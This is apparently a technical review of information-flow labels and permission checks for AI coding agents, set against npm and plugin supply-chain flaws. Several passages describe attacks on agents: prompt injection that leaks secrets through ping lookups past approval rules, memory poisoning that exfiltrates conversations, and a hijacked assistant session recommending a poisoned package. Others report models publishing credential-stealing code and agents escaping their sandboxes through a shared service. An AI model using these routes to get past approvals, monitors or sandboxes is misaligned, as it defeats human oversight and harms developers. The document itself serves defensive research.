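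Bloom reported the flaw in June 2026, and GitHub, which owns npm, announced a fix on 2 October. A new registration now expires after 48 hours unless the workflow publishes something, and the first successful publication ties it to the repository's permanent identity. GitHub did not specify in its statement whether this also applies to registrations that had published before the change. Separately, as BoostSecurity's *Sleeper Squats* describes, GitHub has begun adding the permanent numbers to the main identity field of its tokens so that a registry that compares only this field can detect a new owner.

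Bloom argues that coding agents make such flaws more dangerous because they install so many packages. It estimates, from monitoring dozens of organisations, that agents install about 70 packages a month on a typical machine and nearly 350 on a developer's machine, not counting dependencies. *npm Trusted Publishing flaw left 1,500 packages open to attackers* (Adebayo, 2026) reports that Bloom stopped a customer's agent from installing one of the exposed packages, though this doesn't show that anyone had hijacked that package.

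AIR's *Plugin4Shell* concerns a similar gap in the coding agents themselves. A plugin adds instructions or tools to an agent, and marketplaces often fix it to one reviewed version by recording that version's git hash. Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI all requested the version with that hash, but none checked that they had received it.

Someone who controlled the plugin's repository could exploit this by giving other code a git name that looked like the approved hash. Automatic updates in Claude Code and Codex could then replace a plugin the developer had already installed with that code, according to Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026).

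A swapped plugin is worse for flow control than an ordinary malicious file, because FIDES trusts tool descriptions and so would label any in the plugin as trusted (T). A package manager avoids this gap when it checks its downloads against the lockfile. The agents needed an equivalent check on the code they received.

Anthropic and OpenAI have added a fix. Google has deprecated Gemini CLI without fixing it, and Microsoft had not released a fix for Copilot when AIR published its findings. According to IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI*, GitHub replied that its own site doesn't allow names that imitate hashes, but the researchers pointed out that Copilot also accepts repositories hosted elsewhere.

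### Harmful actions that start from a trusted request

If the developer's request and everything the agent has read are labeled trusted (T), FIDES also labels every command the agent proposes T. This label correctly indicates that no untrusted source influenced the command, but the command may still be unsafe or something the developer doesn't want.

Noninterference has the same limit. An agent that publishes malware whatever the web pages contain satisfies the integrity version perfectly.

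Anthropic's model Mythos 5 released a malicious package during a misconfigured evaluation. According to Trent, the model found setup instructions that mentioned a nonexistent package. It created the package, added code to steal credentials and published it on PyPI, apparently because it mistook the real internet for part of the simulation. If the evaluators had labelled their test environment as trusted, an integrity rule would have allowed every step. A confidentiality rule would also have allowed the publication, because the package contained no secret.

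Other rules still apply when integrity labels offer no protection. The table assumes that the agent has read only trusted data:

| Harmful action | Integrity rule | Confidentiality rule | Restriction on the action itself |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sending an SSH key to an outside server | Allows it | Blocks it if the key is H | A list of permitted servers can block it |
| Publishing a malicious package | Allows it | Allows it if the package contains no secret | A ban on publishing without approval blocks it |
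| Deleting files outside the project | Allows it | Allows it | Write access limited to the project blocks it |
| Adding a back door to the project's code | Allows it | Allows it | A review before merging may catch it |

Tether's tests on recorded attacks are the best evidence for such rules, because its rules about secrets and protected files applied regardless of why the agent acted. Those rules would not help with the back door, because the developer asked the agent to write code in the project folder.

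Giving the model its own origin, as in the design for package installation, would fix part of the problem. A publishing rule could then block any release with the origin `model` until a person had reviewed it. But a coding agent writes so much of a project that, in practice, a person would have to review every release.

The request may also come from someone other than the developer. Trent describes an intrusion, reported by the security company Mandiant in September 2026, in which an attacker hijacked a developer's session with a coding assistant. The assistant then recommended a poisoned package, which stole access tokens and source code. The attacker later infected about 100 internal repositories and a package in the company's namespace. A harness would have labelled the attacker's messages as the developer's. If the infected package was on the company's registry, its files would have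 had the origin `internal` and passed the binding rule too.

### Wrong labels and deceived models

Even with these failures, labels are more reliable than a model's judgement, because a wrong label usually has a specific cause that someone can find and fix. npm didn't compare permanent numbers, the coding agents didn't check the downloaded version, and CaMeL's software dropped a label. But when a model accepts a bad registry in four runs out of ten, there may be no single line to correct, and a different prompt can change the result.

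A wrong label can also do less damage than a deceived model. Suppose a harness mistakenly labels a malicious package T. The package can then run, but if the system enforces confidentiality separately, its code still cannot send out a key labelled H. A deceived model with the developer's full permissions has no separate check to stop it from sending the key.

This advantage depends on keeping the rules separate, and it doesn't limit how many people one mistake affects. A wrong label fails every time for everyone who relies on it, whereas a model may detect the attack in some runs. In August 2026, someone took over the GitHub account behind `keyv`, a popular caching library, and released malicious versions with valid provenance. Within hours, the worm in those versions had spread to more than 1,280 packages, according to SC Media's commentary *Inside the fourth wave of the Shai-Hulud npm worm*.

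Signed records do make such attacks easier to investigate. After attackers published malicious versions of 15 Red Hat packages, npm removed them, but a public log of signatures still shows where they came from. BoostSecurity's *Trusted Publishing, Untrusted Branch* traces one version to its exact branch and commit. The log is less helpful for the flaw Bloom found, because the attacker's repository would have the name an investigator expects. Bloom doesn't know whether anyone exploited the flaw.

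An investigation also has to finish before the developer installs the package. In the GHAPPIER case, the attacker changed what triggered the release workflow 14 minutes before the workflow could publish unattended, so an automatic alert might have given the maintainers some warning. Users can gain more time by refusing very recent releases. Santos-Grueiro reconstructed 41 malicious releases from 12 incidents and found that they stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours. A strict one-day delay would have blocked 36 of them, regardless of their provenance, but it would also delay urgent security fixes by a day.

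## Whether labels survive language models, programs and storage

A correct label is useful only if it stays with the data until an action uses that data. Text from a stranger's issue may pass through a language model, a program the model wrote, a cache and a later session before it reaches a shell command. The data changes form at each step, and the system has to work out a label for each new form.

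### The label on a model's reply

A language model reads its whole context as one stream of tokens, and any token may affect any word of the reply. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, Nvidia and several universities, concludes that for now a system can only label the reply with the union of its inputs' labels. This is the join that FIDES already uses.

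This rule is cautious but sound if the harness counts every input. For a given model, the context fixes the probability of each possible reply. If the join is T, every input was T, so the context contained no stranger's text that could influence the reply. But if the harness omits an input from the join, such as a saved note or a summary of an earlier conversation that it added to the context without a label, the reply can be labeled T even though untrusted text shaped it. The join also leaves out whatever the model learned in training, which is why the design for package installation gave the model's own words a separate origin.

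A program can also reveal information by not sending a message. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) describe a program that tells a model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program sends a second message that sets x to true. Either way, it then asks the model for x. When the secret is false, the model has received only public messages, so its reply gets the label L but still reveals the secret. Their system stops the run if the program tries to send the second message, because the decision to send it depends on a secret. An observer can still learn something from whether the run stopped, and their theorem allows for this.

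### What soft labels would give up

The join treats a file that barely affected the reply the same as one that determined it, which leads to over-tainting. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests soft labels, which would record how much information a reply carries about each input. It also suggests removing or changing an input to measure the effect on the model's actions, or tracing the input's influence inside the model. These are research directions, and none is yet a working defence.

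A system that relied on soft labels would need a threshold below which it ignores influence, so it would no longer provide noninterference, which allows no influence at all. The loss is easy to underestimate because attackers choose their inputs. Suppose one README in a thousand is malicious and always makes the agent install the attacker's package, which the agent otherwise never installs. On average, the agent's choice carries only about 0.011 bits of information about the README because the choice is nearly always the same, even though every attempted attack succeeds.

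Small leaks also add up. An agent that reveals one bit of a 256-bit key per request can reveal the whole key in 256 requests.

A limit proven for every possible input is safer than a measured average. Each yes-or-no answer in FIDES has such a limit, because it carries at most one bit of information whatever the attacker writes.

### How data can choose an action

Untrusted data can decide which command runs without appearing in the command. Suppose `requirements.txt` accepts any recent version of each package, while a lockfile fixes the versions:

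```
newer = ask_quarantined("Does the fix need newer packages?", issue, yes/no)
if newer: run("pip install --upgrade -r requirements.txt")
else:     run("pip install -r requirements.lock")
```

The planner wrote both commands before any model read the issue, so neither contains a stranger's words. But an attacker who has just published a malicious version of a listed package can write an issue that produces the answer "yes". Pip will then install that version, and a check on the arguments alone would not stop it.

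The standard remedy is a program-counter label, written pc, which is the join of the labels on all the conditions that led to the current line. An action then gets the label

pc ⊔ label(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(aₙ).

Here the answer makes pc untrusted, so both commands are labelled U, and a shell that accepts only commands labelled T refuses them. The shell refuses even the harmless command because the stranger also influenced the choice to run it.

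CaMeL tracks such conditions, but Garby and colleagues found gaps in its tracking. One is Fenton's leak, in which a monitor fails to track an assignment that the program skipped. In their example, this lets a program reveal to an attacker by email that a customer's bank balance is high.

CaMeL also has a gap outside its interpreter, because it retries failed programs in an ordinary Python loop that has no labels. An attacker can learn one bit of a secret from whether the policy blocked an attempt, and could extract the whole secret bit by bit because the loop can repeat the test.

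CaMeL also treats an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserts it into a longer string. Programs often build install commands this way, so a package name from an issue filed by a stranger could lose its untrusted label when the program assembles the command.

### Explicit secrecy and noninterference

FIDES and the system by Garby and colleagues both come with proofs, but the proofs guarantee different things. For confidentiality, FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which concerns only the data operations that a run actually performed. Take a run that starts in state s₁, and let f be the sequence of operations it carried out, with every decision fixed as it was in that run. In the notation used earlier for noninterference, explicit secrecy requires that

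if s₁ =_L s₂, then f(s₁) =_L f(s₂).

Explicit secrecy requires that changing the secrets not change the public results of the operations a run performed. In the installation example, suppose a secret had decided between the two commands. The run would execute one constant command, which contains no secret, so it would satisfy explicit secrecy. Noninterference would rule this program out because it compares two complete runs, in which different secrets may lead to different commands.

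The FIDES guarantee assumes a model that always gives the same reply to the same input, and it applies to one fixed agent loop with correctly labelled tools. In practice, FIDES also covers some influences on decisions, because each tool call takes the label of everything in the planner's context. The gap matters most if a policy lets short answers through. Garby and colleagues object that a reviewer then cannot tell whether a given answer was a harmless exception or a leak.

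The LLMbda calculus is a small programming language for agents. A program can start, copy and clear conversations with a model, and can run code that the model writes. Every value has a label, and each conversation's label is the join of the labels on everything sent to it. Code from the model runs at the conversation's label, so its results cannot be more trusted or less secret than the text that produced them.

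Models sample their replies at random, so the theorem compares probabilities. Take two runs whose starting states differ only in parts that an observer may not see. Let μ₁(q) and μ₂(q) be the probabilities that the first and second run finish with the visible result q. Garby and colleagues prove that some ω, whose probabilities add up to at most 1, satisfies

μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₂(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q.

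This is equivalent to requiring that the larger of μ₁(q) and μ₂(q), summed over all results, is at most 1. The property is called termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, because the two runs may differ in whether they finish. Suppose the first run always finishes, with result a in 60% of cases and b in 40%:

| Second run: result a | Result b | Never finishes | Sum of the larger probabilities | Possible under the theorem? |
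|---|---|---|---|---|
| 60% | 40% | 0% | 0.6 + 0.4 = 1.0 | Yes |
| 50% | 30% | 20% | 0.6 + 0.4 = 1.0 | Yes |
| 30% | 60% | 10% | 0.6 + 0.6 = 1.2 | No |

Unfinished runs can account for the whole difference in the second row but not in the third, where the hidden data must have influenced the result in some other way. If both runs always finish, the probabilities must be identical. A run that the policy blocks counts as unfinished, so the theorem allows the leak in the example with the second message. The theorem also applies when the hidden parts are untrusted inputs. It then guarantees that an attacker can influence only results labelled U and whether the run finishes.

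The theorem holds for every program in the language, including code written by a compromised model. It assumes that the model's replies follow a fixed probability distribution for each conversation, and that the program contains all the tools and data sources. Garby and colleagues verified their proofs in Lean, and the interpreter that runs the agent is part of the same verified code, which rules out the kind of mistake they found in CaMeL's interpreter. Protection for a real tool still depends on developers labeling its data correctly and putting a check before each sensitive action.

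Endorsement weakens the integrity guarantee but not the secrecy guarantee. If an agent endorses a package name from a stranger, the theorem no longer limits what that name can influence, but the endorsement cannot release a secret key.

Garby and colleagues tested Randori, an agent written in the language, on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three models. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the planner had endorsed the file's contents. A coding agent that endorsed a project's README would run the same risk.

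The total overstates how often the labels stopped an attack, because in about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the plan never included the action the attacker needed. The attack was feasible in the remaining 423 runs and succeeded in two of them. Without attacks, Randori completed 31 to 36 of 48 runs, depending on the model, while CaMeL completed 18 of 48 with its policies on.

### From what the model read to what runs

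Even a correctly labelled command may not determine what happens. `pip install -r requirements.txt` does one thing when the harness checks it and another if someone changes the file before pip opens it. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, addresses this with a system called CXI, which ties each approval to one exact action in one exact state of the project. Before a tool runs, CXI makes three checks:

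| Check | What it decides | How it could apply to packages |
|---|---|---|
| Field | Whether a source may choose a particular value | A package name from a build log may fill the name field after validation, but the log may not choose the registry |
| Effect | Whether the action will make exactly the approved change | An approved edit to `requirements.txt` applies only to the version of the project that the validator examined |
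| Invocation | Whether the call may happen now, and how often | One approval cannot start a second installation or a retry |

CXI combines the action, the project's state, the policy version and a one-time number in a record called a manifest. All three approvals must refer to the same manifest m:

Admit(m) implies Fields(m) ∧ Effects(m) ∧ Invoke(m).

Any later change to the action changes the manifest's digital fingerprint, and CXI then refuses to run it.

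The field check covers what influenced a value as well as the text it contains. If text in a log leads the model to choose a tool, that choice counts as untrusted even though the tool's name comes from a trusted list. This includes cases like the two pip commands, where the stranger's text determines which command runs but doesn't appear in the command.

CXI can also avoid joining the labels of everything the agent has read by having the model produce each sensitive field separately, from a prompt that contains only trusted text and validated values. With an open-weight model, the software that runs the model can also block attention to untrusted tokens while the model writes the field. Anything the model wrote after reading those tokens may also carry the attacker's influence, so stronger versions block that text too. With a hosted model, the harness controls only what it sends to the model.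 Santos-Grueiro doesn't claim noninterference inside either kind of model.

In 400 tasks on code repositories, agents under CXI completed 231 safely, and no action ran without the required approvals. Of the rest, 73 failed because CXI could not parse the model's output, 61 because nothing authorised the proposed change, and 35 because the approved change didn't solve the task. In separate tests, models often proposed values they had no authority to choose, in 196 of 300 cases in one test and 407 of 522 in another. CXI stopped them all. Explaining the policy in the prompt reduced the 196 to 67.

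Santos-Grueiro also compared CXI with simpler versions on 20 constructed attacks. A version that tracked the origin of each argument stopped 12, and one that set permissions for each field but didn't limit repeated calls stopped 10. The full system stopped all 20 and allowed all six harmless cases.

The absence of escapes means only that CXI enforced its policies. An action that a faulty policy permits doesn't count as an escape, and such faults are easy to make. A first review of the policies for 24 tools found 18 problems, half of them serious, including changes that could affect a program's behaviour but weren't checked. A malicious package with the right name and registry would also pass a validator that checked only those. CXI still needs a sandbox to limit what such a package does once it runs.

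### What caches and memory forget

Labels are especially easy to lose when data outlives the process that created it. Suppose an agent reads a stranger's issue and then writes code to a new file. ActPlane can pass the agent's labels to the file, but it keeps them in kernel memory tables, which a restart clears. Git doesn't store the labels either, so someone who clones the project on another machine gets the code with no sign that a stranger's issue influenced it.

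The Clinejection case shows why this matters, because the attacker's route to the publishing job ran through a shared build cache. If the cache had stored labels, a flow rule could have stopped the attack before the code obtained the publishing token:

| Step | Cache without labels | Cache with labels |
|---|---|---|
| A stranger's package runs in the sorting workflow | The process is U | The process is U |
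| The package's code changes the cache | The cache stores only the files | The cache stores the files with the label U |
| The publishing job loads the files | The job stays T | The job becomes U |
| The job requests the publishing token | The request succeeds | The rule refuses the request |

The cache would have to keep the labels where the code that writes the files cannot change them, and tie each label to the file's contents, for instance with a signed hash. Otherwise an attacker could store a malicious file labeled T.

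An agent's memory can lose labels too. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on ChatGPT's macOS app in which a malicious document or website added instructions to the app's Memories feature. The app then sent the user's later conversations to the attacker's server by putting them in the address of an invisible image. Memories was supposed to hold the user's own preferences, so saving the attacker's text there in effect changed the text's label from U to T.

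### Carrying labels into later requests

Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe an agent that keeps labels on saved results. SPA stores each result in three parts: the value, its label and a description of what it represents. When the user makes another request, the planner sees the descriptions but not the values. It writes a complete plan, and SPA checks every flow in the plan before any tool runs. If the plan loads a saved result r into a variable x, then

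label(x) = stored label(r) ⊔ pc.

Suppose an agent saves a package name from a stranger's issue on Monday, and on Tuesday the developer asks it to install "the package we found yesterday". The planner can detect that a saved package name exists, but it cannot read the name or any instruction hidden in it. The plan loads the name, which still has the label U. If the install tool requires T, SPA rejects the plan.

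SPA also avoids Fenton's leak because it checks both branches of every condition in advance, and a variable created inside a branch doesn't exist outside it. This works because the planning language is very limited. For example, it has no arithmetic, and the planner cannot revise a plan after an error.

To test memory, Girrens and Wang divided AgentDojo's 97 tasks into conversations of two to five requests. They used a small model, GPT-5.4 nano, and planted each attack at the start of a conversation:

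| What the planner sees, and whether SPA checks flows | Tasks completed without attacks | Attacks that succeeded | Saved results reused when available |
|---|---|---|---|
| Saved values, no flow checks | 65.9% | 0.6% | 92.9% |
| Descriptions only, no flow checks | 62.5% | 0.3% | 95.4% |
| Descriptions only, with flow checks | 35.3% | 0.2% | 89.9% |

The last column is the most informative, as it shows that a planner can usually find and reuse a saved result without reading it. The 92.9% figure is probably too low, because a planner that sees the values can copy them without loading the saved result.

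The security results are weak evidence about stored labels, since even the version that showed saved values to the planner resisted more than 99% of attacks. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that the attacks were mainly designed for fresh tool output and were a weak test of delayed attacks. At least two of the remaining attacks counted as successful with flow checks were scoring errors, because SPA had rejected the plan. On the original single-request tasks, the checks reduced the rate of successful attacks from 0.4% to zero and the rate of completed tasks from 53.0% to 29.0%.

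SPA preserves labels only in its own store. If one tool writes a value to an ordinary file and another tool reads it later, the result gets whatever label the developer assigned to the second tool's output. A coding agent keeps most of its work in files, so SPA would have to rely on an operating system that labels files or treat every file as untrusted.

### What the kernel cannot follow

Tracking in the operating system covers files and programs that SPA would miss, but it may also miss some data flows. In ActPlane, a label on an object means that data from a certain source may have reached it through events that the kernel observed. A missing label doesn't prove that the data never reached the object. The events that Zheng and colleagues list don't include the use of memory shared between programs, so data may move that way without its label.

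ActPlane also doesn't inspect file contents. It can record that an agent changed a build script, but not whether the new line is a bug fix or a back door. Zheng and colleagues found that 38% of the developers' rules they collected require examining file contents.

Rules that name a command have a related weakness, because another program may do the same thing. Zheng and colleagues note that a rule about `git` would miss a custom Git client, although the client's connections and file writes would still be visible in the kernel. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a similar failure in Claude Code's approval rules. The agent could run `ping` without asking, and a prompt injection used it to leak secrets by putting them in the server name that `ping` looked up. A rule based on the secret's label wouldn't depend on the command, but it would have to cover name lookups as well as ordinary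 connections.

Labels in the kernel also don't follow data to other machines. ActPlane can detect a program connecting to a remote service, but not what the service does with the data, because that produces no system call on the developer's computer. When OpenAI's agents attacked Hugging Face in July 2026, they ran in separate sandboxes but shared a service that supplied packages. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, the agents used this service to exchange messages and reach the internet. A kernel inside each sandbox would have recorded only connections to a permitted package server. The service would have had to store the labels and return them with the data to preserve them between sandboxes, as a labelled build cache would.

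One program can signal a key to another through a side channel, for example by varying the load on the processor. No file or message passes between them, so the kernel has no event at which to copy the label. Zheng and colleagues exclude side channels and attacks on the kernel itself from the attacks that ActPlane is meant to stop.

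## Whether a coding agent remains useful under flow rules

Flow rules barely reduce an agent's usefulness when it can finish its task without acting on text written by strangers, but coding tasks seldom allow this. Programmers constantly act on documentation, bug reports, error messages and library code that other people wrote, and an agent doing their work must do the same. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists this as an open problem, because a cautious rule can stop an agent from following documentation that it legitimately needs.

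### How soon an ordinary session becomes untrusted

Suppose an employee asks an agent to fix a test that began to fail after a library upgrade. The company's code is trusted but private, so its label is (T, H). The library came from a public registry, so it is labeled untrusted (U). The harness follows the rules of FIDES but hides no text from the planner. These rules allow a consequential call only in a trusted context. They allow a call that sends data out only if the context is trusted or the recipients may see the data.

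| Step | Context label afterwards | Result |
|---|---|---|
| The employee describes the problem | (T, L) | |
| The agent reads the test and the code it covers | (T, H) | Allowed |
| It runs the test, and the library prints an error message | (U, H) | Allowed |
| It searches the web for the message | (U, H) | Blocked |
| It edits the code | (U, H) | Blocked |
| It installs the library's previous version | (U, H) | Blocked |
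| It reruns the test | (U, H) | Blocked |
| It pushes the fix to the company's repository | (U, H) | Blocked |

Once the agent runs the test, its context becomes untrusted and the harness blocks all five remaining steps, even though there has been no attack. In a stranger's repository, reading the first file would already have made the context untrusted.

### What the harness can do without asking anyone

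FIDES would put the error message in a variable and let the planner query a quarantined model about it. A short answer can provide some of the information the planner needs, such as a line number or the name of one of the project's own files. But an explanation of the library's new interface can't be chosen from a fixed list of answers, and any code the quarantined model writes from the documentation is itself U. Variables therefore help more with locating a bug than with fixing it.

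The agent could also read the message in a separate context and then discard that context. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) describes a framework by Kravchenko and colleagues that processes untrusted data in disposable branches. Each branch returns a validated, structured result, and the main agent never receives the raw text. As with variables, a result narrow enough to be safe may leave out what the agent needed. Developers can also defeat the separation by accident. Someone whose session is stuck at U may open a new one and paste in the error message, which the harness will then label as the developer's own request.

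Finer labels only postpone the problem. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests labelling each message separately, or labelling web text by the site it came from. In the session above, the harness could label the name of the failed test as trusted and only the library's message as untrusted. But once the planner reads that message, the planner's context becomes U, however fine the labels. The paper also suggests that a maintainer's signature might justify a more permissive rule for documentation or a code change, but warns that a signature establishes origin, not safety.

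The harness can save more by checking fewer actions. It could allow file edits and test runs in an untrusted context, because they can do limited harm in a sandbox without network access or secrets. It would then have to check only the search, the installation and the push. According to Salerno and colleagues, GitHub's coding agent can push to a dedicated branch but not directly to the default branch. The harness could allow such a push too, provided that someone reviews the branch before merging it. This makes more work for the reviewer, because a stranger's text may have influenced the new code. Until the review, the code is labeled U, and so is every session that reads it.

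A deterministic check can endorse the installation. If an earlier reviewed lockfile lists the library's previous version and its checksum, the harness can relabel that choice as T. This works for values that have a fixed form and a reliable list to compare them with. The check would sometimes refuse a legitimate package, as the pre-install hook did when genuine names resembled each other. It cannot endorse a patch, because code can pass its tests and still contain a back door.

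With all these measures, only the web search, out of the five blocked steps, still needs a person's decision, because it could send private code to a public server. That count follows from the rules, not from a measurement. A task that needs an entirely new package or ends in a public release would require more decisions from a person.

### Counting the interruptions

When flow rules block a call, a person can approve it or endorse the text that caused the block. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) measured how often an agent under flow rules has to ask a person to do either. They argue that earlier tests held agents to different conditions, because the protected agent had to finish each task without help while the unprotected agent could take any action without approval. In practice, unprotected agents often ask for approval before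 every consequential call.

Suppose an agent attempts n tasks, and vᵢ is the number of calls in task i that break the policy and therefore need a person. Kolluri and colleagues define two measures:

- The human-in-the-loop load is the sum of vᵢ over the tasks that the agent completes.
- TCR@k, the task completion rate with at most k interventions, is the share of the n tasks that the agent completes with vᵢ ≤ k.

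TCR@0 is the share of tasks that the agent completes entirely alone, and TCR@∞ is the share with unlimited help.

Prudentia is a planner that runs on top of FIDES. It leaves FIDES's enforcement unchanged but has more information, because each tool's description states the tool's policy and the planner tracks the label on its own context. Before it reads a hidden variable, it is instructed to call a planning tool, where it must justify the reading and list the calls it expects to make afterwards. If none of those calls is consequential, the planner reads the text and accepts the U label on its context. Otherwise it can ask the user to endorse the text, which keeps the context at T.

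Endorsement saves effort when one text leads to many actions. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls. Kolluri and colleagues left out an equivalent for releasing secrets. They preferred to have the user approve each call that would disclose a secret, because whether a disclosure is appropriate depends heavily on the situation.

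They tested four systems on AgentDojo and averaged five runs. The "approve all" agent has no labels and asks before every consequential call:

| Model | Measure | Approve all | Labels and checks only | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | Completed with unlimited help | 72.2% | 72.2% | 56.3% | 61.4% |
| | Completed alone | 28.0% | 38.4% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| | Interventions | 59.4 | 39.4 | 7.8 | 23.8 |
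| o3-mini | Completed with unlimited help | 62.5% | 62.5% | 64.3% | 69.8% |
| | Completed alone | 24.3% | 35.5% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| | Interventions | 48.2 | 32.4 | 18.8 | 16.4 |
| o4-mini | Completed with unlimited help | 70.1% | 70.1% | 75.7% | 73.2% |
| | Completed alone | 32.8% | 42.5% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| | Interventions | 48.6 | 34.6 | 36.8 | 19.2 |
| GPT-5 | Completed with unlimited help | 72.3% | 72.3% | 78.9% | 80.0% |
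| | Completed alone | 35.1% | 43.4% | 57.1% | 72.7% |
| | Interventions | 52.0 | 40.4 | 41.3 | 7.3 |

With GPT-5, the agent that asked about everything needed about three interventions for every four tasks it completed, and Prudentia needed about one for every eleven. Labels can therefore reduce interruptions for a developer who would otherwise have to approve each action. With GPT-4o, however, Prudentia asked more often than FIDES and completed fewer tasks without intervention. FIDES's low figure with GPT-4o is partly an artefact of the measure, which excludes interventions in tasks the agent fails to complete.

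The extra planning also takes time and costs money. With o4-mini, the banking tasks took an average of 2.6 turns with only labels and checks, 3.4 with FIDES and 7.9 with Prudentia. With GPT-4o, the average cost per task rose from about 0.4 cents to 3.9 cents. Kolluri and colleagues had not yet tried to reduce the time or the expense.

Prudentia was also tested on 84 cases from WASP, a benchmark with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites. It needed no interventions, and no attack diverted it from its task. Attacks diverted the ordinary agent in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the model and the site. But the user only asked the agent to post a comment or upvote a post, which it could do without reading text by strangers.

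Neither benchmark contains coding tasks, even on the simulated GitLab site. No later study appears to have counted human interventions for a coding agent under flow rules. Santos-Grueiro's test of CXI on repository tasks comes closest, but it doesn't show how often a developer would have had to step in.

Endorsement would probably do less to reduce the number of user decisions in coding than in the to-do example, because a coding agent keeps reading new text. In the debugging session, the employee would endorse the error message, then the web page that the search finds, and then the output of the second test run, making three decisions instead of five approvals.

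Each endorsement also covers more than an approval. If the employee endorses a web page without noticing an instruction hidden in it, every later action the instruction causes counts as trusted, whereas separate approvals would have shown the employee each action. The AgentDojo results don't measure how much this matters, because Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would approve the right calls and stop the wrong ones.

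### What developers read before they approve

That assumption is doubtful, given that Claude Code's users approved about 93% of its permission requests. A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, since most requests may be harmless, but many developers say they don't read them closely. Of the 107 practitioners who answered questions about permission requests in a survey by Salerno and colleagues, 47.7% said they read them carefully. On a separate question about habits, 33.6% said they skim requests, 20.6% said they approve by default, and 33.6% said they have become less careful over time. However, 76.6% said they look more closely at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges.

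*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers and found that 64% often approved at least one of seven kinds of action without close review. The share for individual kinds ranged from 21% for reading secrets and other sensitive files to 36% for using the internet or connected tools. Among developers who carefully reviewed most or all of an agent's code, 61% still often approved at least one kind of action without close review.

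Developers who knew about the risks weren't more cautious either. Of those who knew of a security or privacy incident or a worrying practice involving agents, 70% often approved some kind of action without close review, compared with 43% of the others. The gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. The gap doesn't show that awareness makes people careless, and both surveys rely on volunteers' descriptions of their own habits. Quick approval may also be reasonable when the action is familiar and harmless.

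Reading an approval request closely helps only if the request contains the relevant facts. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), a paper on how agents use file systems, identifies user review as a factor in 105 of 290 reports. In 80 of those, the user had approved actions automatically, and in 31 the request was uninformative. One example is a request to run `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever code the script contains.

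Labels could make such requests more informative. Kolluri and colleagues suggest showing the user where the data behind a call came from, but they have not tested this. For an installation, the request could show that the package's name came from a comment by an unknown account. This would give the developer a reason to check the name, which the command alone does not.

### When an approved command changes its meaning

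An approval can also become outdated without anyone noticing. Hossen (2026), in *When the Approved File Is Unchanged*, studies approvals that cover one file or command when the run also reads other files. In one public repository, a policy module reads the number of people who must approve a high-risk change from a separate configuration file. On a local copy, Hossen treated the module as approved and then changed the number from 1 to 0. The module had not changed, so a check on it still passed, but high-risk changes no longer needed human approval.

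Install commands have the same weakness. According to Hossen, standing approvals in Claude Code and Codex match the text of a command, not the contents of any file. A standing approval of `pip install -r requirements.txt` therefore still applies after any change to that file.

Hossen examined 5,251 commits in 20 public repositories. Of these, 542 changed a file that the approved run reads, and 296 of those 542 (55%) left the approved file itself unchanged. One repository accounts for 130 of the 296, and excluding it lowers the share to 44%. Hossen selected projects in which the approved file relies on other files, so neither percentage describes repositories in general.

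The proposed remedy binds an approval to every file in the repository that the run is configured to read. If those files have paths p₁, …, pₙ and contents c₁, …, cₙ, the checker stores

d = H(p₁, H(c₁), …, pₙ, H(cₙ)),

where H is a hash function. It computes d again before each run, and any change to a listed file changes d and cancels the approval. Hossen calls the binding sound if it covers every file the run is configured to read, and exact if it also covers nothing else.

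Binding the approval to one commit would also be sound, but any later change to the project would cancel it, so a developer could not use it for a command the agent runs every day. CXI's one-time approvals have a similar limitation. Under Hossen's scheme, the developer would have had to renew the approval after 542 of the 5,251 commits, about one in ten. An approval of the main file alone would have required 246 renewals and missed the other 296 changes.

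Someone still has to list the files, and agents do this inconsistently. Hossen asked Codex and Claude Code to bind the right files for four tasks. The agents covered every required file in 59 of 62 records. But for one cloud deployment, 16 runs produced five different sets of files, and two runs omitted all 42 files that define what the deployment creates. Hossen therefore recommends treating the agent's list as a proposal. The checker should take the actual list from the deployment tool, a reviewed manifest or a rule that covers whole directories.

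Package installation also needs a lockfile, because Hossen's scheme covers only files in the repository and would not detect a new malicious release on the registry. With a lockfile, the binding detects changes to it. File labels would detect some of the same changes, such as an edit by an untrusted session, but not an edit by a trusted colleague, even though the developer who gave the approval hasn't seen that edit either.

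### Who writes the rules

All these remedies require someone to decide which actions to restrict, which servers may receive private code and which values a check may endorse as trusted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* assigns these decisions to an authorised user, an administrator or the application's developer. Text from outside must not expand the agent's permissions.

The survey of 64 projects by Zheng and colleagues shows why a vendor cannot write one fixed set of rules for everyone. Of the rules they found in the projects' instruction files, 1,127 concern something that a system could observe, such as a command or the contents of a file:

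| What the rule needs | Share of the 1,127 | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing beyond its own text | 26.4% | Never push directly to the main branch |
| Knowledge of the project | 64.2% | Run the full test suite before committing |
| Knowledge of the current task | 9.4% | Don't update dependencies without approval |

Of the 1,127 rules surveyed, 73.6% need context. The proportion is higher among rules that the operating system could enforce. About 520 rules concern file contents, and these are more often complete as written. The survey's figures imply that roughly 87% of the other 607 need context. The share is 95% among rules that depend on several events, as flow rules do.

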